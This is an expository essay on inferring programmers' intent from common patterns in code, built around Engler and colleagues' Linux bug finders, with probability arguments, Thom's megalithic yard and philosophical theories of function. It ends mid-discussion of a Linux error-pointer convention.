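# Inferring What People Intended from Statistical Regularities in the Things They Build

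## The question and the terms it needs

Inferring intent from statistical regularities means examining many things people have built, finding what most of them have in common, and treating that as evidence of what the builders were trying to do. Software researchers have used the method since 2001 to find errors in programs. If thousands of programmers do something one way and one does it differently, the exception may be a mistake. The method's advantage is that nobody has to specify beforehand what the program is for. Some researchers in artificial intelligence (AI) have a broader use in mind. If common practice is evidence of what programmers meant, the things people build may also be evidence of what people value, in a form that an AI system could learn from.

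### One lock in a thousand

A program starts as source code, which is text in a language such as C or Python. Trained people can read this text, and another program translates it into operations for a processor. Programmers divide source code into functions, which are named blocks of instructions that each do one job. To use a function, a programmer writes a line containing its name where the job needs doing. When the running program reaches this line, known as a function call, the computer carries out the function's instructions and then goes on to the next line.

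Lock and unlock are two such functions. Russell's *Unreliable Guide To Locking*, a manual for the core (or "kernel") of the Linux operating system, explains their purpose with two tasks that each add one to the same counter. If the counter is at 5 and both tasks read it before either writes, both write 6 and one of the additions is lost. To prevent this, each task calls lock before it uses the counter and unlock when it has finished, and any other task that needs the counter has to wait in between. If the programmer forgets to call unlock, the other tasks may wait forever.

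Suppose a large program calls lock in 1,000 places, and a call to unlock follows in all but one. These figures come from *Bugs as Deviant Behavior* (Engler, Chen and colleagues, 2001), which introduced a bug finder built on this kind of counting. What can a reader conclude about the programmer who wrote the exception?

The obvious guess is that the programmer forgot, and there are real examples in Linux. *How to find lots of bugs in real code*, by Engler, Chelf and colleagues, reproduces one from the software for a sound card. A function takes a lock and starts its work. If the program using the card has asked not to wait, the function can return early with a code meaning "busy", before it reaches the line that releases the lock. A programmer could easily write this by accident and is unlikely to have wanted it.

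But a lock without an unlock can also be correct. Some functions take a lock and return while still holding it, so that other code can do its work and release the lock later. The Linux kernel documentation's *Compiler-Based Context Analysis* describes a label, `__acquires`, that programmers use to declare that a function does this. Another label switches off the checking for a whole function, and a programmer who uses it must add a comment explaining why that is safe. Without the labels, a function that keeps the lock on purpose looks much the same from outside as one whose programmer forgot the unlock.

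Engler and colleagues write that when thousands of people act alike, "the majority is probably right, and any contradictory action is probably wrong". The claim about the majority is safer, because 999 pairings of a lock with an unlock are unlikely to be a coincidence. The count is good evidence that locks and unlocks belong together, but weaker evidence that a particular programmer who left out an unlock forgot it. The likelihood of that depends on how often programmers forget an unlock and how often they have a reason to leave it out, and neither figure is in the count.

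Engler and colleagues distinguish what code proves about its author's beliefs from what it only suggests. A MUST belief is one the programmer has to have held, given what the code does. For example, a programmer who calls unlock must believe that the lock is closed, or the call would be pointless. A MAY belief is one that the code suggests, though the pattern suggesting it could be a coincidence. A single lock followed by an unlock supports only a MAY belief that the two go together, since any two calls can happen to be near each other. Repetition makes this belief more credible but never turns it into a MUST belief, so the case against the thousandth programmer still rests on a MAY belief.

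### Behaviour, intent and reflective wish

An *artifact* is anything people have made that others can examine without its makers, such as a program, a configuration file (the text that holds a program's settings), or a building. What an artifact does can differ from what its maker meant it to do, and both can differ from what the maker would want on reflection. People often treat the three as the same, mostly without harm, because in ordinary cases they agree.

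Behaviour, intent and reflective wish can differ in the lock case. The function's behaviour is to return with the lock still closed, which anyone can establish by reading the code or running it. Whether the programmer meant it to return that way is a question of intent. Suppose they did, because they wanted to protect the file during a slow write to disk, but they didn't know that this freezes every user's screen for several seconds. The behaviour then matches the intent, but the programmer's reflective wish is for a different design, which they would choose if they saw the frozen screens.

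The gap between behaviour and intent is an old problem in software, and it appears even in tiny programs. *Intent Formalization* (Lahiri, 2026) gives the example of a request to remove duplicates from a list of numbers. Given 1, 2, 3, 2, 4, one program keeps a single copy of each number and returns 1, 2, 3, 4. Another removes every number that occurs more than once and returns 1, 3, 4. Both programs run, and both fit the wording of the request. According to Lahiri, a language model typically writes the first version, because it resolves the ambiguity using patterns in its training data and has no access to what this user had in mind. That reading is the common one and probably the best guess for a stranger's request, but it is wrong for a user who wanted 1, 3, 4. Lahiri concludes that only the user can ultimately judge whether a statement of intent is correct.

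Engineers have to guess at intent anyway. *Agentic AI for Software* (2025) describes human engineers as doing this implicitly throughout their work, asking what a piece of software should do and whether the current code does it. Inferring a program's purpose from that program alone is circular, because its mistakes may be taken as intended. *Seeking Specifications* (2025) treats this danger as a core criticism of automatic methods. Looking at 1,000 places in code instead of one offers some protection, since one programmer's mistake has little effect on the total, but it doesn't protect against a mistake that most programmers share.

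Philosophers have paid more attention to the gap between what people intend and what they would want on reflection. Gabriel (2020), in *Artificial Intelligence, Values, and Alignment*, distinguishes several things an AI system might follow, including a person's instructions, their intentions, the preferences their behaviour reveals, and the preferences they would have if they were rational and informed. He argues that intentions can be clear and still be faulty, because people reason badly or lack information. Behaviour is no more reliable, since people choose things that harm them, and those who have had few opportunities may learn to want little. *The Ethics of Advanced AI Assistants* (2024) gives the example of someone clicking on a link when the click neither benefits them nor reflects what they value.

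The same idea appears in *Claude's Constitution* (Askell, Carlsmith and colleagues, 2026), which describes how the AI company Anthropic wants its Claude models to behave. *Claude's Constitution* accepts a user's reliance on the model when it is the kind "a person would endorse on reflection". A user who asks for a piece of code may be content never to learn how to write it, but an identical request could come from someone who has said they want to improve and who might not endorse relying on the model in this way.

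### Names for the odd one out

A *specification* states what an artifact is supposed to do, and people can judge the artifact's behaviour against it. The Stanford Encyclopedia of Philosophy's *The Philosophy of Computer Science* gives the example of a phone app. The users' intention is to be rid of annoying calls from call centres. The specification requires the app to keep a list of call-centre numbers, update it at set intervals, check each incoming call against it and block the matches. An app could meet this specification and still let annoying calls through, in which case the fault lies in the specification.

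A *corpus norm* is the way people usually do something across a large collection of artifacts. On its own it is only a description, not a specification. The philosopher Raymond Turner, whose account the encyclopedia follows, distinguishes the two by what gets corrected when there is a mismatch. People correct a description to fit the system, but they correct the system to fit a specification. Turner calls a specification's authority over the artifact "correctness jurisdiction." When a bug finder flags the thousandth lock, it treats a description of what programmers usually do as a specification that one programmer has violated. No one decided that the norm should have this authority, and most of the debate is about whether it should.

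A *deviation* is a place where an artifact departs from the corpus norm, whatever the reason. A *slip* is a deviation that its maker did not intend and would correct if shown it, like the early exit in the sound-card code. (The encyclopedia uses "slip" more narrowly, for breaches of a programming language's own rules.) A *deliberate exception* is a deviation that its maker intended, like a function with the `__acquires` label.

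A deliberate exception can still be a bad decision, as it was for the programmer who froze everyone's screens. Some deviations are neither slips nor deliberate exceptions. Someone who pasted in a block of code without reading it may have had no intention about the unlock at all, and may not care when a colleague points it out. Anyone who sorts deviations by hand will find a few like this.

### Counting a tool's mistakes

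A *code check* is a program that looks through source code for places that break a rule, usually without running the code. To check locks, it starts at each call to lock and follows every path the computer could take to the end of the function, including the branches where the code tests a condition. It tracks whether the lock is closed, and prints a warning if a path ends with the lock still closed. *How to find lots of bugs by checking program belief systems*, by Engler, Chen and colleagues, gives an example from Linux in which a few lines of code take a lock and, under a certain condition, print "free!" and return without unlocking, which produces the warning "missing unlock!".

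The checker needs a rule to check the code against. In a project like Linux, as Engler and colleagues describe it, the rules come from the uncoordinated work of hundreds or thousands of developers, and hardly anyone documents them. Finding them by hand is slow and has to be repeated for each new release. Counting patterns in the code is another way to find them.

If the warning is right, a developer makes a *bug fix*, a change to the source code that removes the error. Here the fix would be one added line that calls unlock before the early exit. Projects usually keep a dated record of all such changes, so researchers can see years later which lines developers thought worth correcting. A fix is about the best evidence that the original code was a mistake, though developers also change code for other reasons.

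A *false alarm*, or false positive, is a report of an error where there is none. It may come from a deliberate exception, or from a checker following a path that the program would never take when run. The invented figures below describe a checker that examines 10,000 places in a program, 50 of which contain real errors.

| | Real error | No error | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Checker reports it | 30 | 10 | 40 |
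| Checker stays silent | 20 | 9,940 | 9,960 |
| Total | 50 | 9,950 | 10,000 |

*Precision* is the share of a tool's reports that are real errors, here 30 out of 40, or 75%. *Recall* is the share of the real errors that the tool reports, here 30 out of 50, or 60%. A checker that printed only its 10 highest-confidence warnings might reach 100% precision, but its recall would then fall to 20%.

The 10 false alarms are a quarter of all the reports, which a developer will notice, but only about 0.1% of the 9,950 sound places, a figure that makes the tool look more accurate. Precision is much easier to measure than recall. Someone can find the precision by reading the 40 reports, but finding the recall requires knowing about the 20 errors that the tool missed, and nobody has that list for a large real program. Researchers therefore plant errors of their own or use errors that developers have already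 fixed, and either choice affects what the resulting figure means.

The column headings also depend on a judgement, because somebody had to decide that those 30 places were real errors. If the makers weren't available, that person was guessing at intent too.

### From finding errors to specifying values

AI alignment is the work of getting AI systems to act according to what people want and value. Part of it is *value specification*, which means stating what people want in a form that developers can build or train an AI system to pursue. This has proved hard even for toy problems. Gabriel recalls a boat-racing game in which developers trained an artificial player to get the highest score. The player went in circles collecting points and never finished the race.

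Much of the difficulty comes from what people leave unsaid. Shah, Krasheninnikov and colleagues (2019), in *Preferences Implicit in the State of the World*, point out that a designer has to specify what a robot should do and also the far larger range of things it should not do. A person who sends a household robot to the far door doesn't think to tell it not to break the vase on the way. Askell and colleagues make a similar point about programming help. A user who wants a bug fixed probably also wants the program to stay in the same language, but might not mention this even if asked about their goals.

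People often build things to serve wishes they forget to mention. An unbroken vase in a room that people walk through suggests that they have been taking care not to break it. Shah and colleagues base a proposal for learning values on this kind of inference. A collection of software looks like a richer record than the room, because it contains millions of small decisions about what to protect and whom to keep waiting.

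The two hopes need very different amounts of evidence, however. With the invented checker above, a programmer reads 40 warnings, throws away 10 and loses perhaps an hour. An AI system that acted on 40 inferred wishes with the same precision would go against people 10 times, possibly with nobody reading the list first. The bug finder also has to establish only intent, and the person who wrote the line can often settle that by looking at it. Value specification has to establish the reflective wish, often of people who are absent or who disagree with one another. It also has to rule out other reasons why a practice becomes common, such as that it was cheap or that everyone copied it from the same place. The AI system would need less evidence if it asked people about the wishes it inferred before acting on them, because a person would then check its inferences as the programmer checks the warnings.

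The evidence on both hopes comes from probability theory, field trials on operating systems, studies of how predictable buggy code is, audits of false alarms, cases where the rare pattern was right, experiments with language models, and reports from working developers. It also includes proofs, simulations and philosophical arguments about inferring people's preferences from what they leave behind.

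## What a rare pattern can show in principle

The rates of slips and of deliberate exceptions determine the chance that a deviation is a slip, and the count of locks gives neither rate. The number of people who follow the corpus norm doesn't directly affect this chance, which is surprising, because a large majority makes a deviation look wrong.

### Slips against exceptions

Let *s* be the rate of slips and *d* the rate of deliberate exceptions, each as a share of all the places where the norm could apply. Leave aside the few deviations that are neither. Deviations then make up s + d of all places, and the chance that any one of them is a slip is

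s / (s + d)

This is a simple case of Bayes' theorem, the rule for revising a probability given new evidence. Every slip and every deliberate exception produces a deviation from the norm. Seeing a deviation therefore rules out the places that follow the norm, but does not change the ratio of slips to exceptions.

Suppose that s is 0.2% and d is 1.8%. Of 10,000 places that take a lock, 9,800 release it in the usual way, 180 keep it on purpose and 20 keep it because the programmer forgot. A checker that flags all 200 deviations is right about only 20 of them, a precision of 10%, even though the norm holds 98% of the time. The first row below uses these figures, and the other rows vary them.

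| Places that follow the norm | Slips (s) | Deliberate exceptions (d) | Chance that a deviation is a slip |
|---|---|---|---|
| 98% | 0.2% | 1.8% | 10% |
| 98% | 1.8% | 0.2% | 90% |
| 99.98% | 0.002% | 0.018% | 10% |
| 99.7% | 0.2% | 0.1% | 67% |

All these rates are invented, though some real tools that learn from common usage have had a measured precision near 10%.

The last row shows how a dominant norm can help identify slips. If someone knows from other evidence that programmers forget an unlock 0.2% of the time, and the norm holds in 99.7% of places, then only 0.1% of places are deliberate exceptions, and two deviations in three are slips. Engler and colleagues rank their warnings partly by how dominant the norm is, using the z statistic. That ordering makes sense if programmers forget all rules about equally often and differ mainly in how often they have reason to break them. This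 assumption is plausible for rules of similar difficulty, but counting can't confirm it, because a count gives only the sum of s and d.

The share of flagged places that are slips probably also falls as a program ages. Developers fix slips that testing and users' complaints reveal, but they have little reason to remove a deliberate exception that works. If they find and fix 16 of the 20 slips, the checker's next run will flag 184 places, of which only 4, or 2%, will be slips.

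### Evidence beyond the count

Further evidence is easier to take into account if the probability of a slip is written as odds. Twenty slips against 180 deliberate exceptions gives odds of 1 to 9 that a deviation is a slip. A piece of evidence multiplies these odds by its *likelihood ratio*, which is how probable the evidence would be if the deviation were a slip, divided by how probable it would be if the deviation were deliberate. A ratio of 9 makes the odds even, and a ratio of 81 makes it 90% probable that the deviation is a slip.

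A missing comment could help distinguish slips from deliberate exceptions, because programmers don't explain things they did by accident. Suppose a project has 20 slips and 180 exceptions, and its programmers are careful enough that only 18 of the exceptions have no comment, along with 18 of the slips. A missing comment is then 9 times as likely beside a slip as beside an exception, and a place without a comment has even odds of being a slip. If the programmers explained only half of their exceptions, 90 exceptions would have no comment, and a missing comment would be much weaker evidence of a slip.

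Names can help too. Whoever wrote a function called `get_locked_buffer` probably wanted it to return with the lock held. Nearby code may be better evidence than either. If a function has five exits and four of them release the lock, it is hard to think of a reason for the fifth to keep it. The fifth exit also departs from the programmer's own practice, not just from that of strangers.

The most direct evidence of what a maker intended is the maker's own answer. *The Interpretation of Texts, People and Other Artifacts* (Dennett, 1990) agrees that asking almost always works for everyday things, since the person who wrote a shopping list knows what it means. But the philosopher Daniel Dennett describes umpiring a baseball game in which he jerked up his thumb, the signal for "out", while shouting "safe". When the players asked which he had meant, he didn't know. He settled on the shout because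 he had more practice at speaking than at hand signals, and anyone watching could have reasoned the same way. A programmer asked to explain a line of code they wrote five years ago may likewise know no more than an observer about what they intended.

Written labels also don't always make the intention clear. Dennett's stepladder has "THIS IS NOT A STEP" printed on its paint shelf, which leaves little doubt, but he also imagines a bottle with a faded label that could read "for feeling faint" or "for peeling paint". Comments in code can become outdated when someone changes the code without updating them.

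### Twenty copies and one witness

Two hints with a likelihood ratio of 3 each give a combined ratio of 9 only if they are independent. A name and a comment that the same person wrote in the same minute are partly the same evidence, so multiplying their ratios counts some of it twice. The same caution applies to the norm itself, where the numbers are larger and wrongly assuming independence can produce a very large error.

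Suppose someone wants to know whether one function call has to come before another, and each programmer who independently works out the order multiplies the odds that it does by 3. Twenty such programmers multiply the odds by 3 to the power of 20, or about 3.5 billion. If instead one programmer worked out the order and 19 others pasted in the result without thinking about it, the 19 would have done so whether or not the order mattered. Their copies therefore leave the odds unchanged, and all 20 programmers together multiply the odds by only 3.

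Most cases lie between complete copying and complete independence. Survey statisticians use the formula n / (1 + (n − 1)ρ) to calculate how many independent observations a group of n similar ones is equivalent to, where ρ (rho) is the correlation between members of the group. For a group of 20, the formula gives 1 when the correlation is 1, about 2 when it is 0.5 and about 7 when it is 0.1, so even a weak common influence removes most of the evidence. Besides pasting the same code, programmers may have learned from the same textbook, started from the same company template or used the same AI model.

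Copying can make a pattern look more widely intended than it was. Kernel developers have copied bugs along with the code around them, and a mistake that appears in 20 places starts to look like a convention. Similarly, one person's deliberate exception, copied 20 times, looks like a choice that 20 people considered separately. Counting how many times a pattern arose independently would be better than counting its occurrences, but that requires the code's history, which its current text doesn't contain.

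### Whether anyone meant the regularity

The arithmetic so far assumes that people meant to follow the norm. But a regularity can also arise by chance or as a side effect of something else. A dispute in archaeology shows how hard it is to rule out these explanations when the makers are long dead.

Alexander Thom surveyed hundreds of prehistoric monuments built of large stones (megaliths) in Britain and Brittany. Most were in ruins, so he looked for patterns in the pooled measurements. In *Megalithic astronomy* (1966), he reported that builders all over Britain had used a standard unit of 2.72 feet, which he called the megalithic yard. He found that they sometimes divided it into four but never into three, and that they often used ten megalithic yards at a time for longer distances. In *Megaliths and Mathematics* (1966), he called the megalithic yard "a very precise unit of length".

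If builders laid out the radius of a stone circle in whole megalithic yards, its diameter would be a multiple of 5.44 feet. Statisticians call a hidden unit like this a *quantum*. The difficulty is that nobody knew its size beforehand, and a researcher who tries enough sizes will eventually find one that fits. The statistician D. G. Kendall (1974), in *Hunting quanta*, took up the problem using Fourier analysis, a branch of mathematics that deals with repeating cycles. The method scores each candidate unit q against the N measured diameters X₁ to X_N with a cosine statistic:

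φ(q) = √(2/N) × [cos(2πX₁/q) + cos(2πX₂/q) + … + cos(2πX_N/q)]

The cosine is 1 when a diameter is a whole multiple of q, and −1 when it falls halfway between two multiples. If there is no quantum, the positive and negative values roughly cancel, and φ varies around 0 with a standard deviation of about 1. If 100 diameters were all exact multiples of q, φ would be about 14. Errors in building and surveying lower it quickly. With a typical error of a quarter of q, the expected value of φ falls to about 4, and with an error of half of q it falls to 0.1, which is too small to distinguish from chance.

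Chance alone produces a φ above 2 about 2% of the time for one unit chosen in advance, but it produces at least one such value about 90% of the time across 100 unrelated candidate units. Kendall therefore tested whether the highest peak over the whole range of candidates was higher than the highest peak that chance would produce.

With a large sample, the theory of random curves can show how high the peaks would get by chance. Kendall used only the diameters of circles, which reduced his sample. Thom had also fitted egg shapes, fans and other figures to the stones, but fitting an egg to a ruined ring requires decisions that could favour the unit. To make up for the smaller sample, Kendall added Monte Carlo runs, in which a computer generates many artificial data sets. Some had no quantum, to show how high the peaks get by chance, and others had one built in, to check whether the test would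 detect it.

Thom's measurements had done well on an earlier test by the statistician Broadbent, so their regularity needed an explanation. But Kendall thought that no test could be decisive until researchers agreed on which data to use. Even a clear peak wouldn't show what had caused it. Other researchers have suggested that the builders paced out their circles, so that the megalithic yard is the average length of a step. Because people's legs are of similar length, builders who had never heard of one another would have produced similar spacings. They would have meant to walk a certain number of steps, not to use a national standard of 2.72 feet. The measurements are better evidence for a rough common spacing than for Thom's very precise unit.

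Some editing programs insert the same lines whenever a programmer starts a new file, so those lines appear in thousands of programs even though the programmers never chose them.

### Purpose and frequency

These problems rest on the question of whether frequency has anything to do with purpose at all. Philosophers have mostly argued about this in biology, where body parts seem to be for something although they have no designer.

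In *Health as a Theoretical Concept*, Christopher Boorse (1977) defines the normal function of a body part as its "statistically typical contribution" to survival and reproduction among members of the same species, sex and age group. He defines a disease as an internal state that reduces some ability below its typical efficiency. If a squirrel's tail catches in a crack and this keeps the squirrel out of the path of a car, protection from cars doesn't become a function of squirrels' tails, because tails don't typically do this.

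Frequency alone isn't enough to identify a function or a disease. Hearts make sounds as regularly as they pump blood, but only the pumping helps keep the animal alive. Unusual traits aren't always diseases, either. Red hair is uncommon but harmless, and a long-distance runner's heart is uncommon because it works better than most. A bug finder that followed Boorse's theory would report a rare pattern only if the code did its job worse than usual.

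Ruth Millikan's *In Defense of Proper Functions* (1989) defines a thing's function by its history instead. Roughly, a thing has a *proper function* if it is a copy of earlier things that did something, and exists because they did it. Millikan's *Biofunctions* adds that proper functions "do not correspond to averages or regularities". The Stanford Encyclopedia of Philosophy's *Supplement to States of Affairs* gives the example of human sperm, which have the function of uniting with an egg although very few ever do. Millikan's own examples include animal displays. Perhaps most mating displays attract no mate and most distraction displays distract no predator, but those are still their functions. She also argues that typical behaviour can't explain why a broken can opener is still a can opener. It can't open cans, and resembling things that can isn't enough, since driftwood may look just like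 an oar without being one.

Millikan allows that things people make can get their functions from the maker's purpose, so a line of code can have a function that no other program shares. The 19 programmers who pasted in the code without thinking don't provide independent evidence that it is correct, but on her theory, if people kept copying it because it prevented lost updates, that history is evidence of what the code is for.

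Boorse (2024) gives a good answer about sperm in *Wakefield's Harm-Based Critique of the Biostatistical Theory*. He points out that about 300 million sperm can't all fertilize the same egg, so he takes the whole ejaculate as the unit with a function. He also notes that a medical handbook counts a sample as normal even if up to a quarter of its sperm are dead. Garson and Piccinini (2014), in *Functions Must Be Performed at Appropriate Rates in Appropriate Situations*, propose a repair to Boorse's theory that could also cover the displays. They define dysfunction as the inability to perform a function at an adequate rate in the right situations, and one success in ten may be an adequate rate for a display.

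Boorse's account has more trouble with defects that everyone shares. In 1977 he conceded that doctors regard tooth decay and hardened arteries as diseases although nearly everyone has them, and he proposed an extra clause to cover damage from the environment. A mistake that most programmers make raises the same difficulty, because a bug finder that relies on counting would report the code of the few who got it right.

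Boorse's theory also depends on the choice of comparison group. Elselijn Kingma's *What is it to be healthy?* (2007) argues that he can't defend his claim that who is healthy can be determined without value judgements. The choice matters just as much in code. Suppose that the 180 deliberate exceptions in the lock example all belong to a group of 200 functions that prepare data for other functions to use. Keeping the lock is the norm in that group, since 90% of its functions do so. Among the remaining 9,800 places, only the 20 slips keep it, so a checker that compared each function with its own kind would raise no false alarms there. But somebody has to decide what the kinds are, and deciding after seeing the warnings would bring back the problem that Kendall avoided by leaving out the eggs.

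Under both theories, it is hard to say where dysfunction begins when the difference is one of degree, such as how long a program may hold a lock. Peter Schwartz (2007), in *Defining Dysfunction*, argues that neither the history of selection nor the present distribution satisfactorily separates low but normal function from dysfunction. Boorse himself accepts that the cut-off is a convention.

Millikan's critics make a strong case that it seems odd to define the heart's function by its evolutionary history, since William Harvey worked out what the heart does two centuries before anyone knew about natural selection. Millikan replies that she isn't analysing what people have in mind when they use the word "function". Her definition is like the statement that water is H₂O, which is true even though people recognised water long before they knew any chemistry. She accepts that a thing's present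 abilities are an excellent sign of its function, much as red litmus paper is a sign of acid. This concession matters in practice, because frequency could be a useful sign of purpose even if purpose consists in something else. The question would then be how reliable a sign it is.

Another objection concerns things that spread without doing any good. The philosopher Buller recounts Peter Godfrey-Smith's example of the segregation distorter gene, which disrupts sperm formation so that 95–99% of the working sperm carry it. This disruption explains why the gene survives, so it seems to meet the historical definition of a function, but biologists don't call it the gene's function. Code that spreads because it comes first in search results has a similar history.

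Dennett's approach is different and can work with a single object. In 1900 divers found the Antikythera mechanism, an ancient Greek assembly of bronze gears, in a shipwreck. According to Dennett, it was almost certainly a model of the planets, and the proof is that it would have been a good one, because the gears turn at rates that fit what Greek astronomers knew. By the same reasoning, an object that would be very bad at removing cherry stones probably isn't a cherry-pitter. Dennett argues that we assume good design whenever we interpret an artifact.

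A programmer might assess the missing unlock by checking whether another function releases the lock later. If one does, the design makes sense and the exception is probably deliberate. If nothing ever releases the lock, the code would serve hardly any purpose well, and a slip becomes much more likely. One such check could easily supply a likelihood ratio above 9.

The fact that an artifact suits a purpose well doesn't prove that anyone designed it for that purpose. Dennett notes that old flat irons now make better bookends than irons, and that an obsolete mainframe computer makes a fine boat anchor. Critics conclude that people need to know the maker's intention to tell what an artifact is for. Dennett replies that the inventor is just another user, whose intention may be only of historical interest once others have found a better use. That is a reasonable view of what an artifact is for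 now, but it is less helpful for finding slips, which depend on what the maker intended.

Assuming good design can also hide mistakes. Dennett describes biologists who respond to an apparently poor design by looking for a constraint they missed, and he defends this as a way to learn more about the animal. Someone who read code this charitably would find a reason for every missing unlock and never report a bug. Inferring preferences from behaviour is difficult for the same reason, because an odd choice can come from an unusual goal or from a mistake in pursuing an ordinary one.

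## Field trials on operating-system code

Engler and colleagues avoided many of these difficulties by trying to establish less. Their bug finders only had to detect that two pieces of code couldn't both be right, or that one piece differed from many others. This didn't require determining what the code was for.

Dawson Engler, David Chen, Seth Hallem, Andy Chou and Benjamin Chelf of Stanford tried their checkers on Linux and on OpenBSD, another free operating system. They checked recent releases, so the errors they found were ones the developers had missed. Much of the code was device drivers, which control hardware such as sound cards. Hardly anyone owns all the hardware needed to run these drivers, but the checkers could analyze the code without running it. In 2000 the group had checked Linux using rules they wrote by hand. When they inferred the rules from the code instead, they found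 ten to a hundred times as many, including all the handwritten ones.

### Rules with gaps in them

The researchers still had to supply part of each rule as a *rule template*, a general rule with gaps called *slots*, such as "A must be paired with B". Putting lock in slot A and unlock in slot B produces the lock rule. Other templates were "lock L protects variable V" and "function F must be checked for failure". The checker searches the code for functions and variables that could fill the slots, so one template can produce many rules that nobody wrote down. Templates are still in use. *One Bug, Hundreds Behind* (2025) sorts 135 security rules for Linux, drawn from developers' past fixes, into 14 templates.

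### When code contradicts itself

Some actions in code leave no doubt about what the programmer believed. Someone who divides by a number must believe that it isn't zero, and someone who releases a block of memory must believe that nothing will use it again. Engler and colleagues also assume that programmers don't write pointless code, so anyone who tests a condition must think it could be true or false. These are MUST beliefs. If two conflict, at least one is wrong, and the checker can report an error without knowing which. Liu and Böhme (2026), in *LLM-based Code Auditing by Inferring and Evaluating Developer Assumptions*, have revived belief inference with language models, but in 2001 a person had to list the actions that implied each belief.

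The simplest of these checkers dealt with pointers. A pointer holds the address of something in the computer's memory, and a program follows the pointer to reach what is stored there. A null pointer leads nowhere, and following one can crash the whole system. Here are four lines from a Linux driver for digital telephone lines, put into plain words:

```
1: if card is null, then
2:     print an error message that includes
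3:         the number stored where card points
4: end of the "if" block
```

The checker keeps a list of beliefs about each pointer, and at the start its list for `card` is empty.

- Line 1 tests whether `card` is null. The programmer must therefore have thought that it might be. The lines inside the block run only if it is, so the checker records "null" for them.
- Line 2 starts to print an error message, which implies nothing about `card`.
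- Line 3 follows `card` to look up a number for the message. This implies that `card` is not null, which contradicts the recorded belief, and the checker prints a warning.
- Line 4 ends the block. After it, `card` could be either null or not null.

The programmer wanted to print a helpful message about a missing card, but printing it would crash the kernel. Readers can see the mistake without comparing this driver to others.

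The same contradiction can occur in the opposite order, as when a serial-port driver follows a pointer and tests three lines later whether it is null. Either the test is pointless or the earlier line can crash. A third version of the checker looks for tests whose result is already determined by earlier code. In a graphics driver, a programmer requested two areas of memory but tested the first pointer after each request, so the code would miss a failure of the second.

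Contradictions can also be deliberate. Kernel programmers often test for a condition that should be impossible and, if it occurs, call `panic`, a function that restarts the machine. The code after the test appears to follow a null pointer, but the machine restarts before that code runs. Engler and colleagues removed hundreds of false alarms with a 16-line addition that recognised such calls. They also set an admittedly arbitrary limit of about ten lines between a use and a later test, because a test a few lines later is probably a mistake, but one 100 lines later may be sensible caution.

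Another checker looked for security holes. Ordinary programs pass pointers to the kernel, and a malicious program can pass a harmful one, so kernel programmers use special functions to copy the data safely. A programmer who uses one of these functions must believe that the pointer is unsafe, and one who follows the pointer directly must believe that it is safe. The researchers extended this reasoning to groups of functions that do the same job in different drivers. In one group, 55 functions treated a pointer as unsafe and two followed it directly. A single careful function would have been enough to expose those two.

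### Counting when nothing is certain

The pattern behind a MAY belief could be a coincidence, so the checker treats every candidate as if it were a rule and records how often the code follows it. To find unchecked failures, for example, it assumes that every function can fail, then checks whether the program tests the result of each call before using it. If almost every caller of a function tests the result, the few that don't are suspicious.

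The researchers rank the resulting warnings by a score called the z statistic:

z(n, e) = (e/n − p₀) / √(p₀(1 − p₀)/n)

Here n is the number of places where the rule could apply, e is the number that follow it, and p₀ is the share that would follow it in a typical case, usually set at 0.9. The score measures how far the observed share is above p₀, in units of the variation that chance would produce in a sample of that size.

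For 999 of 1,000 places, the observed share is 0.099 above p₀, and dividing by 0.0095 gives a score of about 10.4. For 9 of 10 the score is 0, and for 3 of 4 it is −0.15 divided by 0.15, or −1. The last case is an invented example in which a program uses one variable four times, three of them while holding a lock. The program uses a second variable three times, only once while holding the lock. The second variable scores about −3.3, so the lock more plausibly protects the first.

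Ranking patterns by percentage would put one that held in its only case above one that held 999 times out of 1,000. The z statistic gives the first pattern a score of only 0.3.

Engler and colleagues also give part of a real ranking, from a checker that tried to infer which Linux functions release memory. If programs rarely use memory after passing it to a function, the function probably releases it, and any later use may be an error. The published scores fit a p₀ of 0.5. The table adds the scores for 0.9, which are much lower but in the same order.

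| Function | Places checked | Exceptions | z with p₀ = 0.5 | z with p₀ = 0.9 | Researchers' verdict |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| `kfree` | 2,623 | 60 | 48.9 | 13.2 | Real error |
| `kfree_skb` | 1,070 | 13 | 31.9 | 9.6 | Real error |
| `page_cache_release` | 117 | 3 | 10.3 | 2.7 | False alarm |
| `dev_kfree_skb` | 109 | 4 | 9.7 | 2.2 | Real error |
| `cmd_free` | 18 | 1 | 3.8 | 0.6 | Real error |

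The false alarm in third place is understandable. `page_cache_release` drops one reference to a page of memory, and the kernel frees the page only when no references remain. Most callers don't use the page again, but a caller that holds another reference can safely keep using it.

At first the researchers chose a minimum score and treated every belief above it as a MUST belief. They got too many false alarms when the minimum was too low and found nothing interesting when it was too high. Ranking the warnings and reading down from the top worked much better.

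### What the counts measure

The table below gives the published results. The last column is the precision among the reports that the researchers counted.

| What the checker looked for | Method | Bugs | False alarms | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Pointer found null, then followed (check-then-use) | Contradiction | 79 | 26 | 75% |
| Pointer followed, then tested (use-then-check) | Contradiction | 102 | 4 | 96% |
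| Redundant tests | Contradiction | 24 | 10 | 71% |
| Unsafe use of user pointers | Contradiction | 35 | 19 | 61% |
| Unchecked failures | Counting | 195 | 37 | 84% |
| Memory used after release | Counting | 23 | 11 | 68% |
| Missing second call, such as unlock | Counting | 23 | 11 | 68% |

The 61% figure excludes five of the 35 bugs because they came from an earlier Linux version for which the researchers had no count of false alarms. Among the unchecked failures, 116 of the 195 bugs involved functions the researchers hadn't known could fail. Counting revealed that these functions needed checks, so it found bugs that a checker with a handwritten list would have missed.

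The researchers ranked their warnings, started with the most promising and stopped when false alarms became too common, so these percentages don't give s/(s + d), the chance that a deviation picked at random is a slip. If a checker produces 1,000 warnings and someone finds 70 bugs in the best 100, the precision is 70% for those 100 but could be anything from 7% to 97% for all 1,000. For memory used after release, the researchers looked only at the 14 highest-ranked functions. The first two functions in their published ranking had 73 exceptions between them, but the results for this checker cover only 34 reports.

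The researchers also judged for themselves what counted as a bug, and they acknowledged that an outsider could mistake correct code for an error. As a safeguard, they reported almost all of the bugs they found to the main developers. Many of the reports led to fixes, including all of those about user pointers.

### The error behind a false alarm

One false alarm led the researchers to an error they ranked among the worst of the more than a thousand they had examined by hand. The error involved `seg_alloc`, a function that sets up memory for several programs to share, in a Linux version from shortly before the 2.4 release.

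Many kernel functions return a pointer if they succeed and null if they fail. When `seg_alloc` failed, it instead returned an error code encoded as a pointer. Washington University in St. Louis' *Linux Kernel Code Error Checking* explains that this works because valid pointers never use the highest addresses, so the kernel can use those values for error codes. Callers have to test for them with the function `IS_ERR`. The convention was deliberate, and a comment in the *Linux kernel mirror (for testing)* source code describes it as a scheme for returning either an error code or a normal pointer.

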